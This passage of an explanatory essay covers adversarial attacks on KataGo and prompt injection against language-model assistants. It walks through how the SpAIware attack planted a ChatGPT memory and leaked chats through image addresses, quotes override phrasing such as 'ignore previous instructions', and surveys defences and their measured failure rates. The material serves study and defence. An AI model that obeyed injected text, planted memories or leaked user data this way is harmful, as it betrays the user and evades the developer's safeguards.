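The second defence was a nine-round arms race. In each round, KataGo played 18% of its training games against the latest adversary and the rest against itself, then the adversary trained against the improved KataGo. With a modest amount of search, the final KataGo lost only a few percent of games to the adversaries it had trained against. It still lost often to the next adversary, and to another that had never played the intermediate versions. Both used rings that differed in size, position or the stones inside. A person who knows how to answer one of these attacks can almost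 certainly answer the others, but KataGo's training against some attacks did not carry over to others.

For the third defence, Tseng and colleagues used a vision transformer instead of a convolutional network. KataGo's convolutional network combines information from neighbouring points layer by layer, which fits Wu's account of the miscounting, while a vision transformer can relate distant points directly. They trained the transformer from scratch through self-play until it reached the level of top professionals, and it won two of three games against professional players. A retrained adversary still beat it, and Pelrine found it the easiest of the defended programs to beat by hand.

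| Defence | Attack | Positions per move | Attacker's wins | Attacker's training compute, relative to the defended program's |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ring positions, December 2023 | Gift | 512 | 91% | 6% |
| Ring positions, December 2023 | Ring | 4,096 | 65% | 13% |
| Ring positions, May 2024 | Ring | 4,096 | 75% | 9% |
| Ring positions, May 2024 | Ring | 65,536 | 56% | 9% |
| Nine-round arms race | Ring, next adversary | 4,096 | 59% | 26% |
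| Nine-round arms race | Ring, next adversary | 65,536 | 42% | 26% |
| Nine-round arms race | Ring, separate adversary | 512 | 81% | 5% |
| Nine-round arms race | Ring, separate adversary | 4,096 | 4% | 5% |
| Vision transformer | Ring | 65,536 | 78% | 467% |

The last attacker seems to have needed a lot of computing power relative to its target because the transformer had little training and the figure includes the computing power used to train the original adversary. Retraining that adversary for the transformer took less computing power than training the transformer.

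*Bridging Local and Global Knowledge via Transformer in Board Games* (2024) tested a network that combines convolutional and transformer designs. Tseng and colleagues describe it as more robust than a convolutional network of similar size, but still vulnerable. *A Study of Solving Life-and-Death Problems in Go Using Relevance-Zone Based Solvers* (late 2025) still listed the attacks on KataGo among the known imperfections of programs trained this way.

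### Whether more search or training would close the gap

More search helps, and with unlimited search a program would never make a mistake. Wang and colleagues took ten games KataGo had lost and went back to the last position in each where it could still have won. KataGo had examined 1,600 positions per move during the games and chosen a losing move at each of these points. When it examined 500,000, it found a winning move in eight of the ten.

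However, an adversary trained against deeper search learns to set its traps further ahead. In games against KataGo at ten million positions per move, the decisive mistake came about eight moves before the capture, compared with about six at lower settings. Wang and colleagues also took five positions from games that KataGo had lost while examining a million positions per move, and let it examine a billion. It still chose a losing move in all five. Perfect play on a full board is also out of reach. *Solving Go under Positional Superko* (2026) presents a program that proves the outcome of Go on very small boards, but the proofs grow about tenfold with every two or three points added to the board, and a 6 by 6 board is still too large.

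Further ordinary training may make the problem worse. As Tseng and colleagues trained their transformer, and a convolutional network for comparison, both became stronger players but more vulnerable to the ring attack.

There is a better case for more adversarial training. Over the nine rounds, training the adversaries took 18 times as much computing power as training KataGo to beat them. Tseng and colleagues therefore suggest that if attacks could be found faster, a program might be able to train on enough attacks to become fully robust. The arms race also made attacks harder. The separate adversary won only 4% of games when KataGo examined 4,096 positions per move.

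The results for later versions of KataGo are less encouraging. After more than a year of training on ring positions, the May 2024 version, searching 4,096 positions per move, lost 75% of its games against a retrained version of the 2023 adversary. The retraining took less than 1% of the computing power used to train KataGo. A defender who has to learn each variation of an attack separately needs to find nearly all of them, because an attacker can win with any one that remains.

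### Average opponents and chosen ones

Several explanations that might apply to other systems don't fit the ring weakness in Go, which leaves the way these programs learn. The attacker makes only legal moves, so a reference monitor that enforced the rules would block none of them. KataGo's input describes only a board and the rules in force, so no part of it can act as an instruction from a stranger. Sabotage is also a poor explanation, because the weakness appears in programs from separate teams and in a transformer that the researchers trained themselves.

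A program's average performance is its mean chance of winning over some population of opponents, and its worst-case performance is its lowest chance of winning against any possible opponent. If the average is 99.9%, opponents who beat the program at least half the time can make up no more than 0.2% of the population, since a larger share would lower the average. A high average therefore shows that such opponents are rare in the population, but some may still exist, and an attacker can search for one directly.

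In self-play, the program trains against copies of itself. The copies share the same blind spots, so their games rarely test them, even though idealised forms of self-play provably converge on a strategy that no opponent can exploit. A KataGo developer, commenting on *Beyond the Board*, an online article about the defences, explains that rings are too rare in self-play for the network to learn them well, and that what it learns about other large fights does not carry over to them.

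Similar failures occur outside Go. *Robust and Diverse Multi-Agent Learning via Rational Policy Gradient* (2025) describes a program for a game in which two players move around a shared space. The program scored 240 when paired with a copy of itself, but 4.6 when paired with a partner trained to expose its weaknesses. It had come to rely on both players passing each other clockwise.

Tseng and colleagues consider self-play the likely cause, but they do not rule out a problem with deep learning in general. All the programs they tested learned through self-play, so the results cannot separate the two explanations. They suggest training against a varied population of opponents, or using methods designed specifically to produce unexploitable play, which have worked at a high level in the board game Stratego. They also suggest letting a program keep learning while someone attacks it. If one of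 these methods produced a Go program that withstood new adversaries, the fault would lie with self-play rather than with learning from examples in general.

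## Hidden instructions in documents that an AI assistant reads

David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) in December 2025, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a language model to score how well each CV meets a job's requirements. One candidate adds hidden text to their CV, instructing the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. If the model complies, the candidate has given the recruiter's system an order through the CV. A player could not give KataGo an order through a board position.

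*Prompt injection* is text in a language model's input that the model obeys as if it were an instruction from its user or developer. The CV is an *indirect* prompt injection, in which the attacker has no access to the system but writes something that it will later process. People already try this. In *Hiding Prompt Injection in Legal Filing*, Schneier (2026) drew attention to a legal filing that contained hidden instructions for AI. About five weeks later, in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, Mascellino (2026) reported that the security firm Barracuda had found fraudulent emails designed to manipulate both the recipient and their AI assistant.

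### One stream of tokens

Before a language model processes a text, a program cuts it into tokens, which are words or fragments of words, and replaces each token with a number. The model takes the whole sequence and calculates a probability for every token that might come next:

P(*t*ₙ₊₁ | *t*₁, *t*₂, …, *t*ₙ)

The program picks a token, adds it to the end of the sequence and repeats the calculation until the answer is complete. In the recruiter's system, the earliest tokens might be the developer's instruction and the rest the CV. Both are input to the same formula, which has no separate place to mark who wrote what, whereas a parameterised query has a placeholder for the customer's text.

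Willison (2022), in *You can't solve AI security problems with more AI*, traced the problem to the line of code where a developer joins a fixed instruction to untrusted text. Willison, a programmer, wanted suppliers to offer two separate inputs that the model would treat independently. Most suppliers now accept the developer's instructions separately, as a "system prompt", but their software then joins them to the other text in one sequence, with tokens marking each part. The effect of those tokens on the model depends on its training. In a 2024 update, Willison wrote that system prompts had not proved fully reliable.

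Models learn to treat a document differently from a request, and will usually summarise a letter instead of obeying it. But this is a learned tendency, like KataGo's judgement of which groups are safe, and an attacker can look for wording that defeats it. David C lists several attempts to strengthen the tendency, such as marking the data more clearly and training models to prioritise the developer's instructions. In his view, these are all attempts to add a distinction that the technology lacks.

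Filters meant to detect attacks can miss them, because an attacker can phrase the same order in endless ways. Filters can also block harmless text. Willison pointed out that a translation service with such a filter could not translate an article about prompt injection. If the filter is a language model, the attacker can give it instructions too. Willison quoted an attack that asked the "injection detector" to report that no injection had taken place.

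Willison and several others independently coined the term "prompt injection" in the summer of 2022, according to an article in The Economist quoted in Willison (2025). In many early attacks, the attacker was the person using the chatbot, and the damage was slight. In January 2024, the delivery firm DPD switched off its customer-service bot after customers found it would swear on command. The risk grew as developers connected models to websites, email and private files, because an attacker could then write instructions that someone else's assistant might follow.

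### SpAIware, step by step

In 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger showed that a single web page could make ChatGPT's macOS app send an attacker everything the user typed from then on, along with ChatGPT's replies. He describes the attack, known as SpAIware, in Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*. The attack relied on Memory, a feature that lets ChatGPT save notes about a user and draw on them in later chats. OpenAI had introduced Memory that February, according to The Hacker News' *Spyware via Memory Function* (2024).

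In *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), including Rehberger, examined SpAIware and ten other attacks to see which classical security principles each one violated.

The SpAIware attack began when the user asked ChatGPT to read a web page or document that contained the attacker's text. ChatGPT failed to separate instructions from data, so it acted on the text as a command when the user wanted it as information.

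The text contained an instruction to save a new memory, and ChatGPT did so without asking the user. Christodorescu and colleagues classify this as a failure of *tamper resistance*. This was Anderson's first condition for a reference monitor, and they apply it to the whole trusted computing base. ChatGPT relies on its memories as a record of what the user wants, so a stranger should not be able to write to them.

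ChatGPT then used the planted memory in every new chat, so the attacker no longer needed the web page. The memory contained instructions for ChatGPT to include an image from the attacker's server in its answers and to put the user's messages into the image's web address. When the app requested that address to display the image, it sent the messages to the attacker. The image could be invisible, so the user would notice nothing.

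According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, *least privilege* failed at this point because the app could contact any server at any time, even when the user's request didn't require it. *Secure information flow*, which governs where information may go after a program has legitimately obtained it, also failed. ChatGPT needed to see the conversation, but the attacker's server should not have received a copy.

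The history of the leak is a good reason to add *complete mediation* to the failures that Christodorescu and colleagues list. Rehberger had told OpenAI in April 2023 that images could carry data out of ChatGPT. OpenAI replied that this was a feature it did not plan to address, according to SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server*. In December 2023, the company added `url_safe`, a check that decides whether an image's address is safe before ChatGPT loads it.

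Rehberger pointed out a weakness in this check at the time, in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. The web version of ChatGPT had to request the check itself, so OpenAI would have to change every other app separately. The iPhone app did not yet have the check, and neither did the macOS app when OpenAI released it in 2024. Mediation was incomplete because every image request from these apps skipped the check.

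### What the fix changed

Rehberger reported to OpenAI in May 2024 that a web page could plant false memories in ChatGPT. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue rather than a security issue. In June Rehberger sent a demonstration of the complete attack, and in September OpenAI fixed the macOS app by blocking the attack's route through images.

The repair closed the main route for sending data out, but a web page could still plant a memory, and the `url_safe` check still let small amounts of information through. *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT*, an advisory from the security firm Tenable, describes another way to plant memories. Tenable first contacted OpenAI in December 2024, and by November 2025 it had disclosed seven weaknesses in ChatGPT, only some of which OpenAI had addressed (The Hacker News, 2025). Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes another attack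 that planted lasting instructions in ChatGPT's memory. OpenAI fixed the flaw in December 2025. *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) reports four attacks on AI agents that research teams published within about ten days in July 2026, one of which also planted a memory.

OpenAI has since made the check on web addresses much stricter. Rehberger explains in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that ChatGPT may now open an address that OpenAI's web crawler has already found or that the user typed. It may not open an address it has just composed, since that address could contain private data. Rehberger calls this a significant improvement, but warns that small leaks remain possible and that the check does not prevent injection itself.

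Christodorescu and colleagues suggest protecting the memory directly. ChatGPT could ask the user to approve each new memory before saving it, as some other assistants do. It could also screen new memories automatically, but a stored preference and a stored attack are both ordinary sentences, so telling them apart usually requires another learned system, which attackers can also try to fool.

### Four mismatches with classical security

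SpAIware worked partly because OpenAI did not apply principles that were decades old. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that these principles are also harder to apply to *agents*, systems in which a model works through a task by repeatedly calling tools such as a web browser. They identify four mismatches between the principles and agents.

A processor's no-execute bit works every time, so engineers can build other protections on it. A language model that decides which requests to refuse also becomes part of the trusted computing base, but nobody can prove that it will always refuse correctly. Christodorescu and colleagues imagine a model that denies forbidden requests 99% of the time. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, an attacker who made 100 attempts would have about a 63% chance (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰) of succeeding at least once. A real attacker can also learn from each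 failure.

They attribute part of the problem to the random choice of tokens, but this is the smaller part. Even if developers make a model always choose the most probable token, no one can work out in advance which inputs will defeat it. They think it may be impossible to build provable defences on such a model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a later paper from much the same group, avoids this mismatch by treating the model as untrusted, but the other three mismatches remain.

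**Policies that change with the task.** A phone app has a fixed purpose, so its developer can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it. The permissions an agent needs depend on what the user asks it to do. In an example from Christodorescu and colleagues, a user asks an agent to comment on issue 745 on GitLab, a website where programmers track their work. The agent only needs to open that page and write in the comment box. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent still needs to read the page but no longer needs to write on it. Someone would have to fill in the airline's table of users and files again for every request.

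A model could work out the new permissions from the new request. But by then its input also includes text from the issue page, which a stranger may have written to get wider permissions. Clearing the input first would be safe, but the agent would lose everything it had learned from the earlier task.

A phone app requests the user's contacts from the operating system, which can recognise and refuse the request. But an agent that operates a browser may act only through the mouse and keyboard, and a monitor that detects a click at a certain point on the screen cannot determine whether the click opens a menu or sends a payment. Christodorescu and colleagues describe one design that inspects the messages the browser sends to websites, where the meaning of an action is easier to recognise.

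An agent should follow some of the new instructions it finds while working. While summarising issue 745, it may discover that the issue depends on another, and a helpful agent will read that one too. It also has to follow the documentation of its tools. A developer therefore cannot simply forbid an agent to act on what it reads. According to Christodorescu and colleagues, whether a new instruction is a useful change of plan or an attack depends on where it came from and how far it changes the task.

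Web browsers have a similar problem, because a web page can load programs from other sites. The browser records the address each program came from and confines it to a compartment with limited rights. Christodorescu and colleagues find that agents lack both protections. The origin of an instruction is hard to establish, and nothing inside the model reliably confines the instruction's effect.

An attack hidden in a document can closely resemble the work the user asked for. Howard (2026), in *The Attack That Arrived as a Footnote*, gave two AI assistants, Claude and Codex, a five-question algebra quiz and asked for complete worked answers. One version of the file contained a sixth problem that was invisible on the page but present in the text that software extracts. Both assistants noticed something odd about the document but solved the extra problem anyway. A filter looking for phrases such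 as "ignore previous instructions" would have found nothing, because the hidden text was just another quiz problem.

### Whether this is SQL injection again

In both prompt injection and SQL injection, a developer mixes trusted instructions with a stranger's text. But David C considers the comparison dangerous, because developers who know SQL injection will expect a fix as complete as the parameterised query, and prompt injection may never have one.

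David C prefers to compare the model to a *confused deputy*, a program tricked into using its authority on behalf of someone who has less. Suppose the airline has a printing service that is allowed to open any file. A reservation agent who isn't allowed to see the passenger list asks the service to print it. If the service checks only its own permissions, the agent gets the list. The airline can fix this by making the service check the requester's permissions, which works because the system keeps track of who sent each request.

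A language model cannot reliably make that check, because the recruiter's request and the candidate's hidden line arrive in the same sequence. David C therefore calls language models "inherently confusable". On this view, developers can make prompt injection less likely and less harmful but cannot eliminate it, and they should not use a language model where they can't accept the remaining risk.

In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) classify prompt injection as the newest case of a failure that recurs whenever one channel carries both control and data with no structural boundary between them. Old telephone networks sent their control tones down the same line as callers' voices, so a caller could forge the tones. In the buffer overflows of the 1990s, an attacker supplied more data than a program had room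 for, and the excess overwrote the part of memory that controlled the program. SQL injection followed. According to Narisetty and colleagues, engineers solved these problems by building a separation between control and data into the system, not by getting better at recognizing malicious input. The telephone industry, for example, moved its control signals to another channel.

Despite their contrasting titles, the two sides agree on some points. Narisetty and colleagues also say that the SQL fix does not carry over. A database can use SQL's grammar to determine which part of a query is the command, but ordinary language has no such grammar, and training teaches a model to follow instructions wherever they appear. Both sides recommend fixed rules, enforced outside the model, that limit what the system can do. Official advice has also moved towards such limits. *Careful adoption of agentic AI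 services* (2026), joint guidance from the NCSC and agencies in several other countries, recommends never giving agents broad or unrestricted access. Mascellino (2026), in *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*, reported that in August the NCSC urged organisations to isolate agents, supervise them and control their access tightly.

David C writes that prompt injection may never be fully mitigated. Narisetty and colleagues make a stronger claim, that separation between instructions and data cannot be enforced inside the model. They cite measurements showing that neither prompting nor further training reliably produces this separation in current models. Those measurements do not cover models with a different design, such as one with the two independent inputs that Willison wanted.

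The lack of a grammar is only part of the obstacle. The recruiter's software can track exactly which characters came from the candidate, so it could label them perfectly. But the CV is meant to influence the score, unlike a customer's name in a database command, which never changes what the command does. Even with perfect labels, the model would have to let the candidate's text influence its answer without obeying it, and nobody has defined that difference precisely enough for a program to enforce.

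### A feature that is also a flaw

Customers buy language models because the models follow instructions in ordinary language. This suggests that prompt injection is an intentional but non-malicious flaw, meaning a wanted feature that also creates a security hole. Landwehr and colleagues identify one source of such flaws as requirements written without regard to security. "Follow the instructions in the text" is such a requirement if it does not specify whose instructions count. Course notes from the University of Waterloo add that these flaws are often features that the designers intended and implemented correctly. A model that obeys a hidden instruction in a CV is doing something close to what its training rewarded.

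Weber and colleagues observe that designers are usually unaware of flaws in this class. Developers of language models, however, have known about prompt injection since 2022. This knowledge doesn't make the flaw malicious, because they did not add instruction-following to give attackers a way in. Still, anyone who connects a model to private data today is accepting a known risk.

The class fits the model better than the software around it. Landwehr and colleagues put programs that carry out a protected operation without sufficiently checking the requester's identity and authority in a separate category of inadvertent flaws. ChatGPT had this kind of flaw when it saved memories on instructions from a web page. The unprotected macOS app resembles a flaw that Weber and colleagues call *inconsistent access paths*, where a system offers several routes to the same result but checks them differently,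 often because an update changed only some of them. SpAIware therefore combined several flaws, and OpenAI could repair the missing check within months because the repair was in ordinary code.

None of these flaws was a planted backdoor. An attacker needs only a way to get the model to read some text, not a secret key, and Willison noted that anyone who can type English can construct an attack. The memory that SpAIware left behind is closer to a backdoor, since an attacker deliberately placed it in the system and it stayed there. But users could read that memory as a sentence in a list and delete it, as Rehberger advises them to do regularly, whereas nobody can read a backdoor in a model's weights that way.

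Removing the inherent weakness is harder than deleting a memory. A model that ignored all instructions in documents would resist a hidden instruction in a CV, but it could not follow a tool's documentation or work through a quiz. Developers have therefore tried to train models to recognize which instructions they should follow.

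## How far training can stop prompt injection

An *instruction hierarchy* is an order of authority for the texts a model reads. The developer's instructions outrank the user's, and both outrank anything in a web page, email or file. Developers teach the hierarchy by giving a model examples in which a lower-ranking text contradicts a higher-ranking one, and rewarding the model for following the higher-ranking one. This training makes the model more likely to follow the hierarchy, but it doesn't add a boundary between instructions and data. Only tests can show how reliably the model follows the hierarchy, and the results depend heavily on who attacks it.

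### Twelve defences under attack

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defences for language models. The group included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. The inventors of most of these defences had reported that attacks almost never succeeded. But researchers in this field usually test defences by replaying a fixed collection of known attacks, or by running a general-purpose automated attack with little computing power. Nasr and colleagues instead used adaptive attacks. They tuned automated searches to each defence, gave them plenty of computing power, and ran an online competition in which more than 500 people tried to break some of the defences by hand.

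Two of the defences, RPO and Circuit Breakers, target *jailbreaks*, in which the user tries to make the model break its developer's rules. The others mainly target prompt injection.

| Defence | How it works | Success rate of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Special tokens mark off part of the input | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | The user's request appears again after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
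| RPO | An automated search finds protective wording to add | 98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Further training on examples of attacks | 100% |
| StruQ | Further training on examples of attacks | Every case tested |
| MetaSecAlign | Further training on examples of attacks | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | A separate classifier looks for attacks | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | A separate classifier looks for attacks | 71% |
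| Data Sentinel | A trial run checks whether the text stops a model from repeating a secret word | Every case tested |
| MELON | A second run without the user's request exposes actions that come from the document | 95% |

Fixed attacks succeed far less often. AgentDojo, a standard set of tasks for AI agents, includes injections that got past Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching as little as 1% of the time. The reported rate for MetaSecAlign on the same benchmark was 2%.

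Nasr and colleagues gave the attacker generous conditions. Some attacks used a filter's confidence score as feedback, which a stranger sending an email would not see. The defences were also tested on different benchmarks, so the table can't be used to rank them. Still, keeping a defence secret seems to add little protection. Against MELON, the automated search succeeded 76% of the time without knowing how the defence worked, and 95% of the time with that knowledge. People in the competition had limited information and feedback, yet they found a successful attack in every scenario. The automated search succeeded in 69% of the scenarios where the two can be compared.

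Like Howard's hidden quiz problem, many of the texts that got past the filters contained nothing obviously harmful, so stricter filters would also block many ordinary documents. Nasr and colleagues still consider filters useful against unsophisticated attackers.

StruQ, MetaSecAlign and Circuit Breakers train models on attacks that the defences' inventors generated beforehand. Nasr and colleagues compare them to early attempts to protect image classifiers, where training on a fixed or weak set of altered pictures also failed. Madry's adversarial training, which generated new attacks at every step, held up better. The results for the three defences are therefore evidence against training on ready-made attacks, but they do not show what a model could learn from an attacker that keeps improving.

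### Training against an automated attacker

OpenAI has since built such an attacker, GPT-Red, a language model rewarded for writing prompt injections that work. OpenAI trains another model to resist these attacks while doing ordinary tasks, without ignoring legitimate requests. As either model improves, the other's training gets harder. The scheme resembles Madry's, except that the attacker searches through texts instead of small changes to pixels.

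Such training needs far more strong attacks than people can write. In the 2025 study, people did better than the automated search, but OpenAI reports that GPT-Red did better than people. GPT-Red found a successful attack against the model GPT-5.1 in 84% of a set of indirect-injection scenarios that GPT-Red had not trained on, while human testers succeeded in 13%.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card*, a safety report published in September 2026, covers the company's leading model at the time. In OpenAI's internal tests, GPT-6 Astra resisted 99.79% of indirect attacks, up from 96.23%. It resisted 99.99% of direct attempts by users to override the developer's instructions. The 96.23% figure matches TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, which gives an average attack success rate of 3.77% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

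OpenAI also had the security firm Gray Swan test the model with 1,810 attacks selected from its public competitions. The chance that at least one of 15 attempts succeeds in a given scenario fell from 27.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol to 8.5% for Astra.

The failure rate fell by a factor of 18 on OpenAI's own test, but by a factor of about three on Gray Swan's. OpenAI used GPT-Red in both the training and its internal test, so part of Astra's resistance may be specific to the kinds of attack that GPT-Red writes, much as KataGo learned to answer certain rings and still lost to others. This evidence is only suggestive, because one test counts single attempts and the other counts runs of 15. Gray Swan's attacks also date from the first months of 2026, before Astra's release, so nobody designed them for Astra. Fixed collections like this misled the inventors of the 12 defences, and an adaptive attacker might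 do better than 8.5%.

Anthropic's models show a similar trend. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that Gray Swan's attacks succeeded within 15 attempts in 2.0% of cases against Claude Opus 5, compared with 5.5% for the previous model, Opus 4.8. When Opus 5 operated a web browser, no attack succeeded in any of 129 scenarios. If those scenarios were a random sample of real attacks, a true success rate above about 2.3% would be unlikely. But attackers do not choose scenarios at random, and they may need only one that was not tested.

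### What 97.13% measures

Press coverage also gives a score of 97.13% for GPT-6 Sol, a cheaper model in the same family as Astra. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) credits the number to a research blog's analysis of OpenAI's system card, which shows the result as a chart. The card defines the measure as "defender success rate averaged per defender query". Each query is one attempt on the model, so the model resisted 97.13% of attempts on this test and 2.87% succeeded.

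It is tempting to treat 2.87% as the chance that any given attempt works. If every attempt had that chance independently of the rest, an attacker who made 24 attempts would succeed at least once with probability

1 − 0.9713²⁴ ≈ 0.50

Real attempts are not independent, because they share a model and often a task. Suppose that in 2.87% of scenarios every attempt succeeded, and in the rest none did. The average success rate would still be 2.87%, but an attacker who made 24 attempts in a randomly chosen scenario, or even 2,400, would have only a 2.87% chance of succeeding at least once. Sending the same text again also adds little, since the model's weights have not changed.

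Published figures for an older model, Claude Opus 4.6, show how far off the simple formula can be. VentureBeat reports that when the model operated a computer through its graphical interface without extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. If attempts were independent, an attacker would have a 79% chance of succeeding at least once in eight attempts. The measured rate was 78.6% after 200 attempts, evidently because almost nothing the attackers tried worked in some scenarios.

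Dependence between attempts can also help the attacker, who can learn from each failure and keep returning to a weak scenario. An attacker who needs only one success will look for tasks where attacks work more often than average. The chance that at least one of 24 attempts succeeds could therefore be well below or well above half.

The type of task matters as much as the number of attempts. Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. In an experiment Willison describes, 6,000 attempts failed to make an email assistant built on that model reveal a secret. The developer had explicitly told the model never to reveal passwords or run commands because of something in an email.

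OpenAI's card contains a similar contrast for GPT-6 Sol. In one test, an agent doing a browsing task could find a simulated message board full of improper requests, such as one to disclose private information. OpenAI had revised this test repeatedly to provoke failures. In runs where the model found the board, GPT-6 Sol carried out the unauthorised action 11% of the time, compared with 52% for GPT-5.6 Sol and 0% for Astra. A user who knew only the 97.13% would have expected GPT-6 Sol to fail less often.

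OpenAI's percentages measure how a model performs against one attacker in one set of environments. TechRepublic cautions that they are not the probability of a breach in a real product. The percentages are good evidence that training has made current models much harder to fool than earlier ones, but they cannot show that the remaining failures are too rare to matter, because that depends on how many people attack, how well they adapt and what the model can access.

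### The inseparability theorem

Better training may lower these rates further, but Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026) argue in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* that no training, however good, can stop prompt injection completely. Their theorem applies to models that pass trusted and untrusted text through the same layers, as today's language models do, but not to designs that enforce a separation between the two.

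The argument starts with a guessing game. An observer sees one internal representation, meaning a list of numbers that the network computed from some piece of text, and has to say whether the text came from a trusted source. Trusted and untrusted sources are equally likely. The best possible guesser then makes errors at the rate

*P* = ½ (1 − TV)

where TV is the *total variation distance* between the representations that trusted and untrusted text produce. It is 0 if the two kinds of text produce the same representations equally often, and 1 if they never produce the same one. For a finite set of representations, it is half the sum of the differences between the two probabilities.

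Suppose there are only two representations, A and B. Trusted text produces A 95% of the time and B 5% of the time, while untrusted text does the opposite. The total variation distance is ½ (0.90 + 0.90) = 0.90, so the error rate is ½ (1 − 0.90), or 5%. This matches a direct count, since the best guess is "trusted" for A and "untrusted" for B, and it is wrong one time in 20.

For single tokens, the distance is below 1. The word "please" enters the network as the same list of numbers whether a developer or a stranger wrote it. Pant and colleagues compared published system prompts with 50,000 user messages and found that the token frequencies had an overlap of between 0.517 and 0.547 for three widely used sets of tokens. Since the total variation distance equals one minus this overlap, the formula gives an error rate of 26% to 27% for someone who sees only one token.

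By the time a language model determines whether to obey a sentence, its internal states reflect not just individual tokens but also the surrounding text, the sentence's position, and the special tokens that mark where a document begins. The theorem would need these states to overlap as well, which Pant and colleagues assume but do not prove. They reason that complete separation would leave the model unable to process a user's text in the same space as its instructions.

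That reason is weak. Suppose training led a model to keep one of the thousands of numbers in its state at +1 for trusted text and −1 for untrusted text. The two sets of states would then never overlap, so the total variation distance would be 1 and the guesser would never err. The model could still use all the other numbers in the same way for both kinds of text. Nobody has shown that current models do this reliably, and the success of attacks suggests that they do not, but this is a fact about particular trained networks and does not follow from their design.

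Pant and colleagues support the assumption with a measurement. They ran 300 instruction texts and 300 user texts through the model Llama 3.1 8B and calculated the maximum mean discrepancy, a measure of distance, between the two groups of internal states at five layers. It rose from 0.61 at the input to 0.91 at layer 8, then fell to 0.76 at layer 31. They conclude that the groups overlap at every layer, but maximum mean discrepancy does not measure overlap. If every instruction state sat at one point and every user state at another, and the measure's length scale equalled the gap between them, the result would be √(2 − 2e^(−1/2)), or about 0.89, even though the groups would not overlap at all. The texts also came from separate collections, so the distance partly reflects differences in writing style.

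### From no guarantee to an attack

The rest of the proof concerns what the model does with untrusted text. At each layer, the model updates its state at one position by adding up contributions from the positions it can see:

new state = Σ (trusted positions) *α*ⱼ*v*ⱼ + Σ (untrusted positions) *α*ⱼ*v*ⱼ

Here *v*ⱼ is the information from position *j* and *α*ⱼ is the weight it receives. A model could not summarise a document if it gave every word zero weight, so untrusted text can always influence the model's decisions.

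Pant and colleagues then define a security condition for decisions such as refusing a request, using a tool or saving a memory. These decisions may depend on what an untrusted text means, but must not depend on how it is phrased or encoded. The same meaning can be phrased in endless ways and training covers only some of them, so correct behaviour on those examples does not guarantee correct behaviour on the rest.

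This is true, but it does not imply the proof's conclusion that the condition actually fails for some untested phrasing. A model that had learned to refuse every request to use a tool would make the same decision for every phrasing, and so satisfy the condition for that decision. Such a model would be useless for many jobs, but the example shows that finite training does not make a failure certain.

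The condition also differs from resistance to prompt injection. A model that obeyed a stranger's order in every possible phrasing would satisfy it, while one that ignored all such orders might still violate it, for instance by answering a harmless question in English but refusing the same question in an unusual encoding. Even a change in the probability of refusal from 1% to 1.001% would violate the condition.

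The narrower claim that survives is that developers who rely only on training examples cannot certify a model against every attack. This matters to anyone who needs a proof, but we can infer little from it about how hard an attack is to find. If the total variation distance in the guessing game were 0.999998, the theorem would still apply, and the guesser would err once in a million guesses. Encryption with a 128-bit key has no perfect guarantee either, because an attacker could guess the key on the first try, but the chance is about 1 in 3 × 10³⁸, and nobody considers that a practical attack.

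Attackers can often do much better than guess against language models, whereas there are good reasons to think they cannot against encryption. Nasr and colleagues say that a defence that a cluster of processors can break in a day does not have the kind of security encryption has. The case against current models therefore rests on the successful attacks. Llama 3.1 8B and Mistral 7B, both small models by current standards, refused all five kinds of injection that Pant and colleagues tried. The injected text changed the length and tone of some answers, so it did influence the models. Pant and colleagues acknowledge that these changes do not violate their condition, and they cite other people's attacks as evidence that a model's refusal can be turned into compliance.

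*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) proves, under a cryptographic assumption, that there can be language models for which no filter that runs much faster than the model can tell harmful prompts from innocent ones.

### People can be deceived too

According to The Decoder, OpenAI admitted in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved. According to Blockchain News, OpenAI compared the problem in March 2026 to social engineering, in which people manipulate employees by pretending to have authority. Companies already trust employees with confidential files and payment systems, even though a clever email might deceive an employee.

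The comparison with people fits prompt injection better than the other failures so far. A message that looks like a routine office request might fool a new employee as well as a model, whereas people do not mistake a slightly altered photograph for an ostrich, and an amateur Go player can see when a ring of stones is in danger. Much of the inseparability argument also applies to the employee, who reads a manager's instructions and a stranger's email with the same eyes and brain. No course on fraudulent emails can cover every future trick, so if the lack of a guarantee were enough to rule out a language model, it would rule out the employee too.

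Employers limit what one deceived employee can do, for example by requiring a second signature on large payments. OpenAI's check on web addresses in ChatGPT now includes a similar step. If opening an address might leak private information, ChatGPT either shows the user the information that would be sent and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request.

Models differ from human employees in ways that favour the attacker. An employee who receives 200 versions of the same suspicious request will probably become wary and warn colleagues. A model that starts each conversation afresh has no record of earlier attempts unless the surrounding software keeps one. An attacker can also often test attacks in private on the same model that a company uses, which isn't possible with the company's employees. Finally, employees have different habits, but copies of a model share the same weights, so a text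 that works on one copy has a good chance of working on the others.

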